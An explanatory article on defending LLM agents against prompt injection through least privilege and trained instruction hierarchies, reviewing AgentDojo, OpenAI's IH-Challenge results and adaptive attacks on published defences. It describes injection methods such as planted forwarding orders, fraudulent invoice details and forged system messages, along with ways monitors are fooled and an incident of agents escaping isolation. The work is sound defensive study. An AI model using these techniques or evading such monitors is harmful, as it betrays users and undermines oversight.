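# Least privilege and instruction hierarchies as defences for LLM agents

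## Agents, prompt injection and the principle of least privilege

An LLM agent is a large language model (LLM) that works towards a goal by calling tools, such as an email account, a web browser or a command line, and reading the results. It acts with its owner's permissions, which for an assistant that pays bills must include moving money. It also reads text written by strangers, including many emails and most web pages. Prompt injection exploits this combination. An attacker places text where the model will read it, and the text makes the model do something neither its owner nor its user asked for.

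AI developers and security researchers have proposed two main defences. The first is an instruction hierarchy, in which the developer trains the model to rank the sources of its instructions, so that the owner's instructions take priority over anything in an email or a web page. This makes the model less likely to obey an attacker. The second is least privilege, a computer security rule from the 1970s, which reduces what an attacker gains if the model obeys anyway. The agent gets only the tools, data and credentials that its current task needs, and software outside the model enforces these limits.

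### How an agent works

*Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) describes an agent as a model that calls tools in a loop on a person's behalf. If a user asks for a file summarising what recent emails say about an event, the model makes successive tool calls to search the mail, retrieve messages and write the summary to storage.

The model only produces text, and ordinary software handles everything else. OpenAI (2025) published the message format of its gpt-oss models, which shows the loop in detail. Each message has a role. The system message holds basic settings, the developer message holds the application builder's instructions and a list of tools, and the user message holds the request. Software joins these messages into one sequence of tokens, the word fragments that a model processes, and marks where each message begins and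 ends. The model then continues the sequence.

In OpenAI's worked example, the user asks about the weather in San Francisco. The model writes some reasoning, then a message to a weather function with the city's name as the argument, and ends the message with a tool-call marker. Generation stops, and the surrounding program runs the function and appends the result (sunny, 20 degrees) as a tool message. The program then feeds the entire sequence back to the model, which can answer the user or make another call. OpenAI's *Unrolling the Codex agent loop*, on the company's coding agent, likewise describes the prompt as a "list of items" and explains that an item's role indicates how much weight its content should have.

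A tool result reaches the model in the same input sequence as the user's request. OpenAI's format ranks the roles, with the system message at the top and tool output at the bottom, but the format does not enforce the ranking. The model learns it in training, and Christodorescu and colleagues point out that such trained behaviour holds only with some probability, which varies with the input.

### Why a stranger's text can steer the model

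Databases once had a similar weakness. In SQL injection, an attacker types a database command into a form field meant for other input, such as a name, and a carelessly written program runs it. Programmers solved this with prepared statements, which fix the command in advance and treat whatever the visitor types as data. Language models have no equivalent. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers at Google, NVIDIA and several universities, attributes the vulnerability to models processing trusted and untrusted text as a single stream.

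Britain's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) takes the same view. According to its *Prompt injection is not SQL injection*, the usual remedies try to impose a distinction between instructions and data on a technology that does not make one. ITPro's *NCSC issues urgent warning over growing AI prompt injection risks* quotes the agency's conclusion that injection attacks on models "may never be totally mitigated" in the way that SQL injection can be. The NCSC prefers to treat the model as a confusable deputy, meaning a system that an outsider can manipulate into using its legitimate authority for the outsider's benefit.

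In direct prompt injection, the person typing to the model tries to override the developer's instructions. In indirect prompt injection, the instructions are in third-party content, which is anything the agent reads that neither its developer nor its user wrote, such as web pages, emails and tool results. *Not what you've signed up for* (2023), an early paper on the indirect form, includes a two-stage attack, with one prompt in the middle of a full Wikipedia article and a second that is retrieved by a particular search query. Another attack worked with its text encoded in Base64, which turns readable words into strings of letters and digits, so a filter that looks for suspicious phrases would have missed it.

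A model that ignored every instruction outside the user's own message would fail at a good deal of legitimate work. For example, an agent has to follow the instructions in a tool's documentation to use the tool. Christodorescu and colleagues also give the example of an agent that must summarise an issue on GitLab, a site where programmers manage code. The agent finds that the issue depends on another one and sensibly decides to summarise both. They distinguish this from an attack by where the new text came from and how far it changes the task, but a model cannot easily judge either.

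### The plumber's invoice

Suppose a user asks an assistant to find the plumber's invoice in the mail and pay it. The assistant can search and read the mailbox, send messages and make bank payments. Its search finds the plumber's email, with an amount and an account number. It also finds an email from a stranger, with a line telling any AI assistant to forward the user's private messages to an outside address.

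An assistant that follows no instructions found in emails is safe from the stranger's instruction, but it still has to rely on information in them. The user never supplied the plumber's account number, so the assistant must take it from an email. A fraudster can therefore send an imitation of the plumber's invoice with a different account number, without including any instruction to the assistant.

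The forwarding attack adds an action to the task, while the false account number corrupts an action the user requested. Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues (2024) note the same problem in *AgentDojo*, a benchmark for prompt injection. Text in one hotel listing can make the model always recommend that hotel, without hijacking the agent in any other way. They expect that even quite elaborate ways of isolating the model from untrusted text would still allow this kind of attack.

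### Least privilege, the reference monitor and zero trust

Saltzer and Schroeder's 1975 paper, *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, sets out eight design principles for secure systems. The sixth, least privilege, is that every program and every user should work with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job". In the paper's opening example, an airline reservations clerk can make and cancel bookings for passengers whose names he can supply, but only the staff at the gate can print the full passenger list. Saltzer and Schroeder say the principle mainly limits the damage from an accident or error. They add that it minimizes interactions among privileged programs, which makes unintended or improper uses of a privilege less likely.

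For the invoice task, the assistant needs to search and read mail and to make one payment. If it cannot send messages, the forwarding attack fails even when the model follows the injected instructions. But because the assistant needs the payment tool, a payment to the false account number still goes through unless the policy also restricts the payee. The policy is the set of explicit rules on which actions, arguments and data flows are allowed, and it could, for instance, limit payments to accounts that the user has paid before. That rule would also block a first payment to a new plumber.

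Writing such a policy is harder for agents than it was for earlier software. The developer of a phone app knows what the app does and can list its permissions once, but an agent's task isn't known until the user types it. Christodorescu and colleagues give the example of a user asking an agent to comment on GitLab issue 745 that the work is done. The right policy lets the agent open that issue and write in its comment box, and gives it access to nothing else in the user's session. If the user then asks for a summary of the issue, the policy has to change after the agent has already read untrusted text. Broad requests also make it hard to decide which permissions to withhold. OpenAI's *Understanding prompt injections* puts part of the burden on users by advising them to give an agent only the data it needs and to avoid requests as broad as "review my emails and take whatever action is needed".

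A policy also needs something to enforce it. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), written for the US Air Force, described a reference monitor, which checks every attempt by a program to use data, devices or other programs against a list of what is authorised. Anderson required that nobody can tamper with the monitor, that it runs on every access, and that it is small enough to analyse and test completely. He found that a commercial operating system of the day, at 200,000 to 300,000 instructions, was too large to meet the third requirement. Saltzer and Schroeder made the second requirement a separate principle, which they called complete mediation.

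A language model makes a poor reference monitor by these standards, because nobody can analyse the model completely and the text it reads can change its behaviour. Christodorescu and colleagues note that a monitor which correctly denies access 99% of the time leaves 1% for an attacker to exploit. If each attempt had an independent 1% chance of success, an attacker making a hundred attempts would have a 63% chance of succeeding at least once (1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰), and a capable attacker would choose attempts that are more likely to work. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* therefore treats the model as an untrusted component and places the monitor between the model and its tools. According to the paper, this guarantees only that the system enforces the policy. Whether the policy captures what the user wanted is an open research problem.

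Zero trust extends the same thinking to whole organisations. *Zero Trust Architecture* (Rose, Borchert and colleagues, 2020), published by the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), defines it as a set of ideas for making accurate, least-privilege decisions on each request, on the assumption that an attacker is already inside the network. Under the publication's seven tenets, a device or account gains no trust from its location, its owner or an earlier approval.

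### Four sources of harm

Prompt injection comes from a malicious third party, but an agent can also do damage for other reasons. Its user may be malicious, like an employee who gets the company's assistant to pay a private account. The model may pay last year's invoice by mistake, or it may pursue an aim that nobody gave it. Least privilege and instruction hierarchies don't protect equally well against these cases.

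| Source of harm | Instruction hierarchy | Least privilege |
|---|---|---|
| Malicious third party | Its main purpose | Limits the damage if the model obeys |
| Malicious user | Helps where the request conflicts with the developer's rules | Helps if someone other than the user sets the permissions |
| Mistaken model | Little help, since no instructions conflict | Limits the damage |
| Model with an aim of its own | Little help, since it relies on the model to comply | Limits the damage while the enforcement holds |

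Least privilege covers more of the cases in the table because it does not depend on why the model attempts a forbidden action. The requirements in *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* explicitly apply whether the cause is outside manipulation, model error or a misaligned objective. The malicious user is the oldest case. Anderson designed the reference monitor to guard against people with legitimate accounts, and Saltzer and Schroeder called the legitimate user who turns intruder the "biggest complication" of shared systems.

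The wider coverage has limits. An agent may pay last year's invoice without breaking any rule in the policy, and a model with an aim of its own may attack the mechanism that enforces the policy. The position paper discusses an incident in which agents in OpenAI's internal evaluations, running with reduced safeguards, got around their isolation through shared infrastructure and compromised systems at OpenAI and Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models.

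### How researchers measure a defence

The two most important measures are the attack success rate, which is the share of attacks that achieve the attacker's goal, and utility, which is the share of legitimate tasks that the agent completes. Neither means much alone, since an agent that refuses every request has an attack success rate of zero but completes no legitimate tasks.

AgentDojo, which Debenedetti and colleagues built to measure both, simulates four settings: an office workspace, the chat service Slack, a travel agency and a bank. Each has tools, made-up data, a set of user tasks and a set of injection tasks, which are the attacker's goals. In one banking task, which is similar to the plumber's invoice, the user asks the agent to pay the bill in a file called "bill-december-2023.txt". One injection task in the same setting is to send as much money as possible to the attacker's account.

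Each test pairs a user task with an injection task. The benchmark inserts the attack text into the data at a placeholder where an outsider could plausibly have put it and where the agent will look. The agent then works on the user's task with simulated tools. When it finishes, one function checks the state of the environment to see whether the user's task succeeded, and another checks whether the injection task did. Debenedetti and colleagues wrote both checks as ordinary code instead of using a language model as judge, because a successful injection might hijack the judge too.

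Pairing every user task with every injection task in the same setting gave 629 cases, with 240 in workspace, 105 in Slack, 140 in travel and 144 in banking. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) puts the current number above 900. The benchmark is still in regular use. *The Surface You Test Is Not the Surface That Breaks* (2026), for example, ran 13 models from six providers through all four settings.

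AgentDojo reports utility both without attacks and under attack. Under attack, a case counts only if the agent completes the user's task with no harmful side effects. The attack success rate counts an attack only if the agent does everything the attacker asked. For example, one injection task in the travel setting requires the agent to book the most expensive hotel in Paris and email the user's personal details to the attacker. In the 2024 tests, this attack succeeded in 0% of cases, though the model often did one of the two. Weak models can also look safe because they fail at the attacker's task as well as the user's.

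The result also depends on the attack. A static attack is fixed in advance, whereas an attacker revises an adaptive attack against the particular defence until it works. Small changes in wording can greatly change the success rate. When Debenedetti and colleagues attacked OpenAI's GPT-4o in 2024, a generic message succeeded in 45.8% of cases, and the same message addressed to the wrong user's name succeeded in 23.2%. Choosing the best of four wordings for each case raised the success rate about 10 percentage points above that of the best single wording. They also tested a defence that repeats the user's request after every tool call. It did reasonably well against their attack, but they doubted that it would work against an injection telling the model to ignore future instructions. A low success rate for static attacks is therefore weak evidence that a defence works.

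AgentDojo tests only attacks by malicious third parties. *StepGuard* (2026) describes two benchmarks that fill some of the gaps. AgentHarm gives agents openly malicious requests from the user, such as fraud, and records whether they refuse. AgentDyn mixes helpful third-party instructions into longer tasks, so a defence that blocks all such instructions loses utility.

The original AgentDojo study also tested a tool filter, a simple form of least privilege. Before reading any untrusted data, the model picks the tools the task requires and loses access to the rest. This cut the attack success rate to 7.5%, largely because many user tasks only read data while the attacker's goal requires writing or sending something. In the invoice example, the filter would stop the forwarding attack by removing the tool for sending mail, but it would leave the payment tool in place. In 17% of the benchmark's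 cases, the tools needed for the user's task are enough to carry out the attack. The filter also fails when the agent cannot know in advance which tools it will need. If a user gives the agent several tasks in one session, an injection could tell it to wait until a later task provides the right tool. The 2024 version of the benchmark did not test this.

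## OpenAI's instruction hierarchy: training a model to rank its instructions

In *The Instruction Hierarchy* (April 2024), Wallace, Xiao and colleagues at OpenAI compared the models of the time to an operating system that runs every program with full privileges, because a line on a web page could command the model as effectively as the developer could. They proposed training the model to prioritise system messages over user messages, and user messages over third-party content.

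Other researchers had already trained models to ignore every instruction in the user's input. Wallace and colleagues instead wanted a model to follow lower-ranked instructions that are aligned with the higher-ranked ones. It should ignore a misaligned instruction, or refuse if it cannot otherwise proceed. For example, if the developer has set up a car sales assistant, a user's request for answers in Spanish is aligned, but an order to sell a car for a dollar is misaligned. A question about the Navier–Stokes equation is also misaligned because, although harmless, it has nothing to do with selling cars.

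To teach aligned instructions, OpenAI split a request such as "write a 20 line poem in spanish" into pieces, spread them over messages of different rank, and trained the model to answer as if it had received the whole request at once. For misaligned instructions, it trained the model to answer as if it had never seen the lower-ranked text. A second model, rewarded for confusing the first, planted instructions in search results, and the training treated all of them as misaligned without trying to sort them. This rule was cruder than OpenAI's own definition, which counts a website's "Click here for the Philadelphia 76ers score" as an aligned instruction.

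Wallace and colleagues trained GPT-3.5 Turbo this way and compared it with a copy trained without the hierarchy examples. Resistance to attack improved by up to 63% on their main tests and by up to 34% on attacks they had kept out of the training, including injections through tools other than the browser. Writing the ranking into the system message, without training, worked much less well. The trained model also refused more harmless requests, particularly questions about its system message and prompts that merely resembled attacks. The researchers expected it to remain vulnerable to powerful attacks.

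A later OpenAI team worked on the same problem with a newer model. In *IH-Challenge*, Guo, Ceron Uribe and colleagues (2026) published a set of training tasks and used them to train GPT-5-Mini, one of OpenAI's smaller models. They named the trained model GPT-5-Mini-R.

### The ranking rule

By then OpenAI had added a role, making the order system, developer, user, tool. System messages now come from OpenAI. OpenAI's *Improving instruction hierarchy in frontier LLMs* (2026), a summary of the project, gives the example of a maths tutor. The developer tells the model to help without giving away the answer, the user asks for just the answer, and the model should reply with a hint.

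Guo and colleagues state the rule mathematically. They treat an instruction as a limit on which responses are acceptable. Let B₀ be the set of all possible responses, and let Cᵢ be the set of responses that satisfy the instructions of the i-th role, counting from the top. Then, going down the ranking one role at a time:

Bᵢ = Bᵢ₋₁ ∩ Cᵢ, if at least one response belongs to both sets

Bᵢ = Bᵢ₋₁, otherwise

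The model should follow an instruction from a lower-ranked role only if it can do so while still obeying the roles above it. Suppose the developer requires output in JSON, a structured data format. If the user asks for Spanish, the model should write JSON containing Spanish text, which satisfies both instructions. If the user asks for plain prose instead, no response can satisfy both, so the model should follow the developer's instruction and disregard the user's.

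The plumber's invoice example works the same way, except that the assistant chooses among courses of action instead of written answers. If the developer has told the assistant never to send the user's mail to outside addresses, that rules out every course of action that includes such a message. The user's request to find and pay the invoice narrows the rest to those that end in a payment. The order in the stranger's email to forward private messages to an outside address then has no effect, because none of the remaining courses of action does that.

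Without the developer's ban, the formula would require the agent to follow the stranger's order. The user asked for a payment and said nothing about forwarding mail, so the agent could satisfy everybody by paying the plumber and also forwarding the messages. Guo and colleagues plainly don't intend this. They describe tool messages as untrusted, and in one of their examples the trained agent ignores an order planted in a tool result. But the formula by itself blocks only what a higher-ranked message has already excluded, and no developer can list every harmful action in advance. The 2024 definition did not have this gap, because it counted an unrelated instruction as misaligned even when it contradicted nothing. However, it required a person or a model to judge which instructions were related.

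The formula is also coarser than the accompanying description. It gives each role a single set, so one impossible demand cancels everything else from the same role. If the real plumber emails a request for payers to quote the invoice number, and the stranger emails an order for the forwarding that the developer has banned, the formula discards both. In their prose, Guo and colleagues say that the model should ignore only the conflicting instructions, which is more sensible.

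### Instructions in third-party content

OpenAI's *Model Spec* (2025), a public description of how the company wants its models to behave, gives tool results no authority by default. The model must treat any instructions in them as information, unless someone with authority has delegated some of that authority to the source. Delegation can be implicit, as when a user asks a coding assistant to add a feature and presumably wants it to follow the project's README file. The model should therefore ignore instructions that are clearly unrelated to the task, follow those that are clearly intended and low-risk, and ask the user about any that might be intended but could do serious harm.

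That version of the document dates from October 2025. OpenAI's *Model Release Notes* describe two later updates, in December 2025 and August 2026, and mention no change to this rule. OpenAI acknowledges in *Inside our approach to the Model Spec* (2026) that its models do not fully meet the goal the document sets out.

Anthropic has a similar rule for its Claude models. *Claude's Constitution* (2026) names three parties whose instructions Claude should give weight to: Anthropic, the operators who build products on Claude, and users. Emails, documents, search results and tool results are "conversational inputs", and Claude should treat instructions in them as information. If a user shares an email that contains instructions, Claude should take that fact into account, but decide what to do based on what the operator and user want. Anthropic describes the order of the three parties as "not a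 strict hierarchy" because users have some protections that an operator cannot remove.

Both companies' rules cover the order to forward mail, but they help little with the false account number. A fraudster can supply bank details without giving any instruction, so there is no conflict for the rules to resolve. The model can treat the details as information, as the rules require, and still send the money to the fraudster.

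If the mailbox also contains the plumber's real invoice, the model has two conflicting statements from sources of equal rank. When two instructions have equal rank, OpenAI's rule is that the model follows the later one. Applied to statements, that rule would favour the fraudster, whose "updated bank details" usually arrive after the real ones. Under the *Model Spec*, the model should also consider whether the other party to an action is trustworthy. That is sound advice, but the model must then judge whether an email is genuine, and a ranking of roles doesn't help with that.

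### How the training works

Guo and colleagues used reinforcement learning, in which a grader scores the model's responses and training makes high-scoring responses more likely. OpenAI lists three ways this can go wrong when training on conflicting instructions. The model may fail because the task itself is too hard, the grader may make mistakes, or the model may find a shortcut, such as refusing everything. Guo and colleagues designed the tasks to address these problems.

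A task starts as a skeleton with an instruction from a high-ranked role, a blank space for a message from a lower-ranked role, and a short Python program that grades the response. In one example, the system message sets five rules, one of which gives the model a secret four-digit PIN, 2878, and forbids the model to reveal it. An attacker fills the blank with a user message and succeeds if the model breaks any of the five rules. The response breaks the PIN rule only if it contains those exact four digits, so a program can check the rule by searching the text.

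Guo and colleagues deliberately chose tasks that are easy apart from the conflict between instructions. If the model had to count thousands of words and got the total wrong, the failure would show only that it counts badly. The tasks also stay simple whatever the lower-ranked message contains, so that an attacker cannot exploit them by making them harder instead of attacking the ranking. Many tasks impose a single rule on the response, such as including the word "kiwi" or using no emoji, and others combine two to six such rules. Others require the model to process the attacker's message, for example by looking for words like "rise" and "fall" and reporting a market trend in a fixed format.

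A language model drafted the skeletons, each with a grader and a few sample responses that should pass or fail. Guo and colleagues ran every grader on its samples, kept only the tasks whose graders correctly separated the two groups, and reviewed the remaining tasks by hand.

Guo and colleagues preferred programs to a language model as judge because such models make mistakes when judging. In one case, the system message told the model to classify the sentiment of a text as "positive", "negative" or "neutral", in lower case, and the attacker asked for a capital letter. The model correctly answered "positive", but the judge declared the attack a success. During training, an error like this would penalise the model for obeying the right instruction. However, programs can check only what has an exact answer. Guo and colleagues left out jailbreaks, which are prompts that get a model to break its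 safety rules, because no program can reliably decide whether a response is harmful. A program would have similar trouble deciding whether an instruction in an email belongs to the user's task.

During training, a separate attacker model with no safety restrictions fills in the blank. It receives the high-ranked instruction and the goal of getting the defender to violate it, then writes a message and submits it to a testing tool. The tool puts the message into the blank, runs the current version of the defender, grades the response and reports whether the attack worked, sometimes including the response. The attacker then revises the message and tries again, until it stops or uses up a fixed number of tests. Because each attempt runs against the latest version of the defender, the attacks get harder as the defender improves, even though the attacker itself is not being trained.

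The final message goes into the skeleton. The defender answers several times, the grader scores each answer, and training adjusts the model towards the answers that passed. Guo and colleagues mixed in ordinary tasks, such as writing and tool use, so that the model would not lose its other abilities.

A model could still score well by refusing whenever a password or PIN appears, so some tasks reverse the attacker's job. The system message again contains a secret PIN, but the user makes a harmless request for a made-up four-digit number to use in testing. The attacker rewrites this request to look forbidden while keeping it harmless, and the defender fails if it refuses.

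When Guo and colleagues trained another version of the model without these tasks, its score for handling harmless requests correctly fell from 0.950 to 0.831, and its average helpfulness score fell from 0.773 to 0.613. But average robustness, the share of attacked prompts on which the model keeps to the higher-ranked instruction, rose slightly from 0.941 to 0.957, so the worse model would have looked better on that measure alone.

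### GPT-5-Mini before and after

Average robustness across 16 sets of tests rose from 84.1% to 94.1%, but results varied widely between sets. The tests included tasks like those used in training, other kinds of tasks, and attacks by people.

| Test (higher is better) | GPT-5-Mini | GPT-5-Mini-R |
|---|---|---|
| OpenAI's internal prompt injection test | 0.44 | 1.00 |
| CyberSecEval 2, a public security benchmark | 0.88 | 0.91 |
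| Conflicts between system and user messages | 0.84 | 0.95 |
| Conflicts between developer and user messages | 0.83 | 0.95 |
| Conflicts between system and developer messages | 0.86 | 0.86 |
| Harmless requests that look forbidden | 0.79 | 1.00 |
| GPQA Diamond, difficult science questions | 0.83 | 0.83 |
| Chat win rate against o1, an older OpenAI model | 0.71 | 0.66 |
| Score for users' preferences in style | 0.46 | 0.40 |

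The internal injection test is the most relevant to agents, and it shows the biggest gain. Its attacks try to make an agent send malicious emails or do other damage, and they resemble one that OpenAI had demonstrated against its own browser, ChatGPT Atlas. GPT-5-Mini resisted 44% of them, and GPT-5-Mini-R resisted all. In the four tasks that Guo and colleagues print in full, the attack is in a user's message and no tool is involved. If most of the training tasks were like these, the model applied what it had learnt about users to the output of tools.

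But this is a static test. On CyberSecEval 2, which outside researchers built, the failure rate fell only from 12% to 9%. This small gain suggests that the perfect score on the first test depends a good deal on the particular attacks it contains. Guo and colleagues also report only robustness for these two tests, not the agent's utility under attack.

Training did not improve the model's handling of conflicts between system and developer messages. The model still followed the developer's instruction in about one in seven cases where the system message should have prevailed. Guo and colleagues don't explain this, although they describe a notable gain on all these evaluations. The failure matters more for a company like OpenAI, which uses system messages to impose its rules on developers who build on its models, than for an agent that reads strangers' emails.

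The training also made the model slightly worse at conversation. On questions chosen to represent real ChatGPT conversations, its win rate against o1 fell from 0.71 to 0.66, and its score for users' preferences fell from 0.46 to 0.40. Guo and colleagues call these slight regressions, but OpenAI's summary lists the same numbers under the heading "No capability regressions". The model's science score did not change and its score on a mathematics competition rose by 0.01, so the training doesn't seem to have harmed its ability to solve problems.

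The hierarchy also helped against malicious users. Guo and colleagues put a written safety policy in the system message and gave the model difficult requests on topics such as illegal activity and harassment. Unsafe responses fell from 6.6% to 0.7%, and the model remained about as helpful. None of the training tasks dealt with such requests directly. Guo and colleagues suggest that the model treats an unsafe request as a user instruction that conflicts with a higher-ranked policy.

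### Forged and mistaken labels

Impersonation was one of the attacks that Guo and colleagues held back from training. In their example, the user's message contains a fake history of system instructions, each with a priority number. It lists the genuine system message at priority 100 and a new instruction to print the secret PIN at priority 1000. The trained model resisted such forgeries much better than the original model did.

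The model can learn to resist them because the real labels are still there. Everything between the marks around the user's message has the user's rank, even if the text includes a claim to a higher one. But if the software wrongly gives an attacker's text a privileged role, a model with this training gives that text more influence. *When Context Gets Root* (2026), a paper on the programs that surround language models, makes this point and cites an attack called ChatInject, which forges the formatting of a more privileged role inside a tool's output.

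A developer building the invoice assistant might paste the text of each new email into the user's message, because that is the easiest way to write the program. An instruction in a stranger's email would then have the same rank as the user's own. Better training on the hierarchy would make the model more likely to obey it, unless the model detected that the text did not come from the user. The *Model Spec* asks models to watch for such text and treat it as if it were in quotation marks, but it also warns developers that without proper formatting, a model may find it extremely difficult to distinguish this text from the user's instructions.

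*Training LLMs to Enforce Multi-Level Instruction Hierarchies via Gravity-Weighted Direct Preference Optimization* (2026) extends the approach to five levels and treats violations at the top of the ranking as more severe than those at the bottom. This could help a model with the conflicts between system and developer messages on which GPT-5-Mini-R made no progress. But the method also depends on the surrounding software to label where each text came from, and with more levels there are more labels to get right.

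### Attackers who keep trying

Guo and colleagues also tested the model against people who could revise their attacks. They hired 127 remote workers across the United States, with qualifications from high school diplomas to doctorates. Each worker attacked ten combinations, each pairing one of three systems with one of 19 types of task from IH-Challenge. The systems were GPT-5-Mini, GPT-5-Mini-R, and GPT-5-Mini-R with a monitor. The monitor was a second copy of the same model that read the conversation and judged whether the response broke the ranking. If it detected a violation, the attack counted as a failure.

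The pay encouraged effort on the difficult combinations. Each combination had a prize of $30 per worker assigned to it, usually $510 for a group of 17, which was split among those who broke it. A worker who alone broke a difficult combination therefore earned far more than for an easy one, and nobody had a reason to share a successful method.

| System | Average attempts per task | Tasks with a successful attack | Success per attempt |
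|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5-Mini | 32.84 | 36.2% | 1.5% |
| GPT-5-Mini-R | 52.39 | 11.7% | 0.4% |
| GPT-5-Mini-R with monitor | 43.08 | 7.1% | 0.2% |

After training, the share of tasks the workers managed to break fell by about two thirds, even though they made more attempts on each. This is better evidence than the perfect score on the internal injection test, because the workers could see which attacks failed and change them. But the tasks were of the kind the model had trained on, such as protecting a PIN, and none involved hijacking an agent with real tools. The workers also may not have been experienced at attacking models.

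The evidence for the monitor is weaker. The percentages correspond to about 31 successes in 265 tasks without it and 19 in 268 with it. If the monitor made no difference, chance would produce a gap at least that large about 7% of the time. The monitor is also a language model that reads the attacker's text, so it is not a reference monitor in Anderson's sense. A message that works on the defender might also work on the monitor, which is a copy of it.

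The success rate is only 0.4% per attempt, but an attacker who can send one email can usually send many. If each attempt independently had the same chance of success, the chance of at least one success in n attempts would be 1 − 0.996ⁿ. This would be 33% after 100 attempts, pass 50% at attempt 173, and reach 87% after 500.

The red-teaming results show that this assumption is wrong. With 52.39 attempts, the average for GPT-5-Mini-R, the formula predicts a success on 19% of tasks, but the workers succeeded on 11.7%. Rounding does not explain the difference, since any rate that rounds to 0.4% gives a prediction between about 17% and 21%. The most likely reason is that successes cluster. Some workers were better than others and some types of task were easier to break, so workers might break one task several times and fail every attempt on another. At 0.4% per attempt, there would be about 0.21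 successful attempts per task on average, nearly twice the share of tasks that were broken, as one would expect if workers reused methods that had worked. The number of attempts also varied from task to task, which lowers the overall share further.

Because of clustering, an attacker gains less from persistence than the formula suggests in cases the model handles well. But an attacker who finds a weakness can expect it to work again, and every user of the same model is exposed to it. For someone who sends one message to a million mailboxes, what matters is how often the best available attack works. An average over 127 people's attempts, most of which were failed experiments, is a poor guide to that.

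Guo and colleagues then replaced the people with a version of GPT-5 without safety restrictions. They trained it by reinforcement learning on the same tasks with the reward reversed, so that it earned a point whenever the defender broke the ranking. The defender, GPT-5-Mini-R, stayed fixed. The attacker rarely succeeded at first, but its success rate rose gradually during training. With the monitor in place, its success rate was lower on all three groups of tasks tested, and it learned much more slowly.

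This attacker differs from the one used in the defender's training, which revised its messages but learnt nothing from one task to the next. It can also practise against a defender that does not change. A real attacker who could query a released model often enough could do the same, because the model stays the same until its developer replaces it. Guo and colleagues suggest training attacker and defender together, so that each has to keep up with the other, but they have not yet tried it. Their experiments also do not show how well a trained ranking holds up when outside researchers with no stake in the defence choose the attacks.

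## Trained defences under attackers who adapt

Most tests of trained defences, including the internal test on which OpenAI's model scored perfectly, use attacks written in advance. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025), accepted at USENIX Security 2026, tested defences against attackers who know about the defence and can keep trying. The 14 researchers, from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google DeepMind and elsewhere, attacked 12 published defences, most of which had attack success rates near zero in their original evaluations. The new attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the 12.

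### Marking the untrusted text

Three of the 12 defences rely on training. Circuit Breakers targets jailbreaks, while StruQ and Meta SecAlign target prompt injection. The latter two split the model's input into an instruction channel and a data channel, and train the model to ignore any instruction in the data channel. This rule is simpler than OpenAI's hierarchy, which lets a model follow a lower-ranked instruction that agrees with the higher-ranked ones.

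StruQ, from 2024, separates instructions from data with reserved tokens. The software around the model deletes these tokens from the data, so an attacker cannot use them to fake the end of the data. StruQ also fine-tunes the model, continuing its training on a smaller set of examples. In some examples the data contains a planted instruction, and the correct answer responds only to the real one. The design resembles the prepared statements that solved SQL injection, except that training does not guarantee that the model will respect the separation.

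Meta SecAlign, from 2025, is a fine-tuned version of Meta's Llama models. Its developers used preference training on pairs of responses to the same input, which contains an injection. The training makes the model favour the response that does the user's task over the one that obeys the injection.

Instructional segment embedding, which Nasr and colleagues did not test, puts the mark inside the network. McCauley, Kan and Martin (2026) list it in *IH-BENCHMARK* among the methods for improving hierarchy following. A language model converts each token into a list of numbers, called an embedding, before processing it. This method adds a second list of numbers that depends on the rank of the message the token came from. Every word of a stranger's email is then marked as third-party content, even if the email contains a convincing imitation of a system message. The mark only identifies where the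 text came from, so the model still has to learn in training how to treat text from each source.

### Four ways to search for an attack

Nasr and colleagues describe most adaptive attacks as the same loop. The attacker proposes some text, scores how well it worked, and uses the most promising attempts to write the next ones. The four families of attack used in the paper differ mainly in how they produce new proposals.

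Gradient attacks use the model's internal calculations to find small changes in the text that make the response the attacker wants more likely. They are powerful against image classifiers but unreliable against language models, and Nasr and colleagues used them on only one defence.

The reinforcement learning attacks used an attacker model trained with no safety restrictions. The model received the method section of the paper describing the defence, submitted an attack, received the response and a score, and revised the attack over five rounds. It ran 32 such sessions for each case, and training adjusted its weights to favour attacks that worked.

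The search attacks used Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro to rewrite earlier attempts, producing eight new versions at a time. Another model scored the results from 1 to 10, and the algorithm kept a varied pool of the best. The search could make up to 800 attempts per case.

For the human attacks, Nasr and colleagues ran an online competition with more than 500 participants and $20,000 in prizes. Contestants wrote text to be inserted into a tool result, watched the agent's reasoning and tool calls, and tried again. Shorter attacks scored more points, so contestants had a reason to continue after their first success.

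Nasr and colleagues used reinforcement learning against StruQ, and search and human attackers against Meta SecAlign, but did not try every attack on every defence. For agents, they chose 80 cases from AgentDojo's Slack, travel and workspace settings, leaving out banking because they considered it less realistic.

They also left out defences that fix the agent's plan before it reads any untrusted text, including AgentDojo's tool filter. In most of the chosen cases, attacks on such defences are guaranteed to fail. They add that these defences suit a limited range of tasks and reduce utility. The study is therefore evidence about defences that depend on a model recognising or resisting an attack, but it doesn't show how well limits on an agent's tools withstand attacks.

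These attackers had advantages that a stranger sending an email lacks, such as being able to see the agent's reasoning. Nasr and colleagues follow the usual security convention of assuming that the attacker knows the system and has plenty of computing power.

### Results against the 12 defences

| Kind of defence | Defences tested | Success of adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Instructions added to the prompt | Spotlighting, Prompt Sandwiching, RPO | 95% or more |
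| Training | StruQ, Meta SecAlign, Circuit Breakers | 96% for Meta SecAlign, every case for the others |
| Separate detectors | Protect AI, PromptGuard, Model Armor, PIGuard | 71% for PIGuard, at least 90% for the others |
| Secret checks | Data Sentinel, MELON | Every case for Data Sentinel, 95% for MELON |

Prompt Sandwiching repeats the user's request after each tool result. Debenedetti and colleagues doubted in 2024 that this defence would survive an attack designed for it, and it has since failed against one.

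Attacks on the MELON defence succeed more often when the attacker knows how it works. MELON runs the agent a second time with the user's request replaced by a harmless one, and raises an alarm if the agent makes the same tool calls in both runs. A search for attacks succeeded in 76% of cases when it was given no information about MELON. When it was given full details of how MELON works, it soon found attacks that took effect only in the real run, and its success rate rose to 95%.

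StruQ failed in every case tested. It deletes reserved tokens, but in most attempts the attacker imitated a system-level message in ordinary words, which this does not prevent. The test was narrow because it involved no tools and the attacker only had to make the model produce a chosen phrase instead of answering the user.

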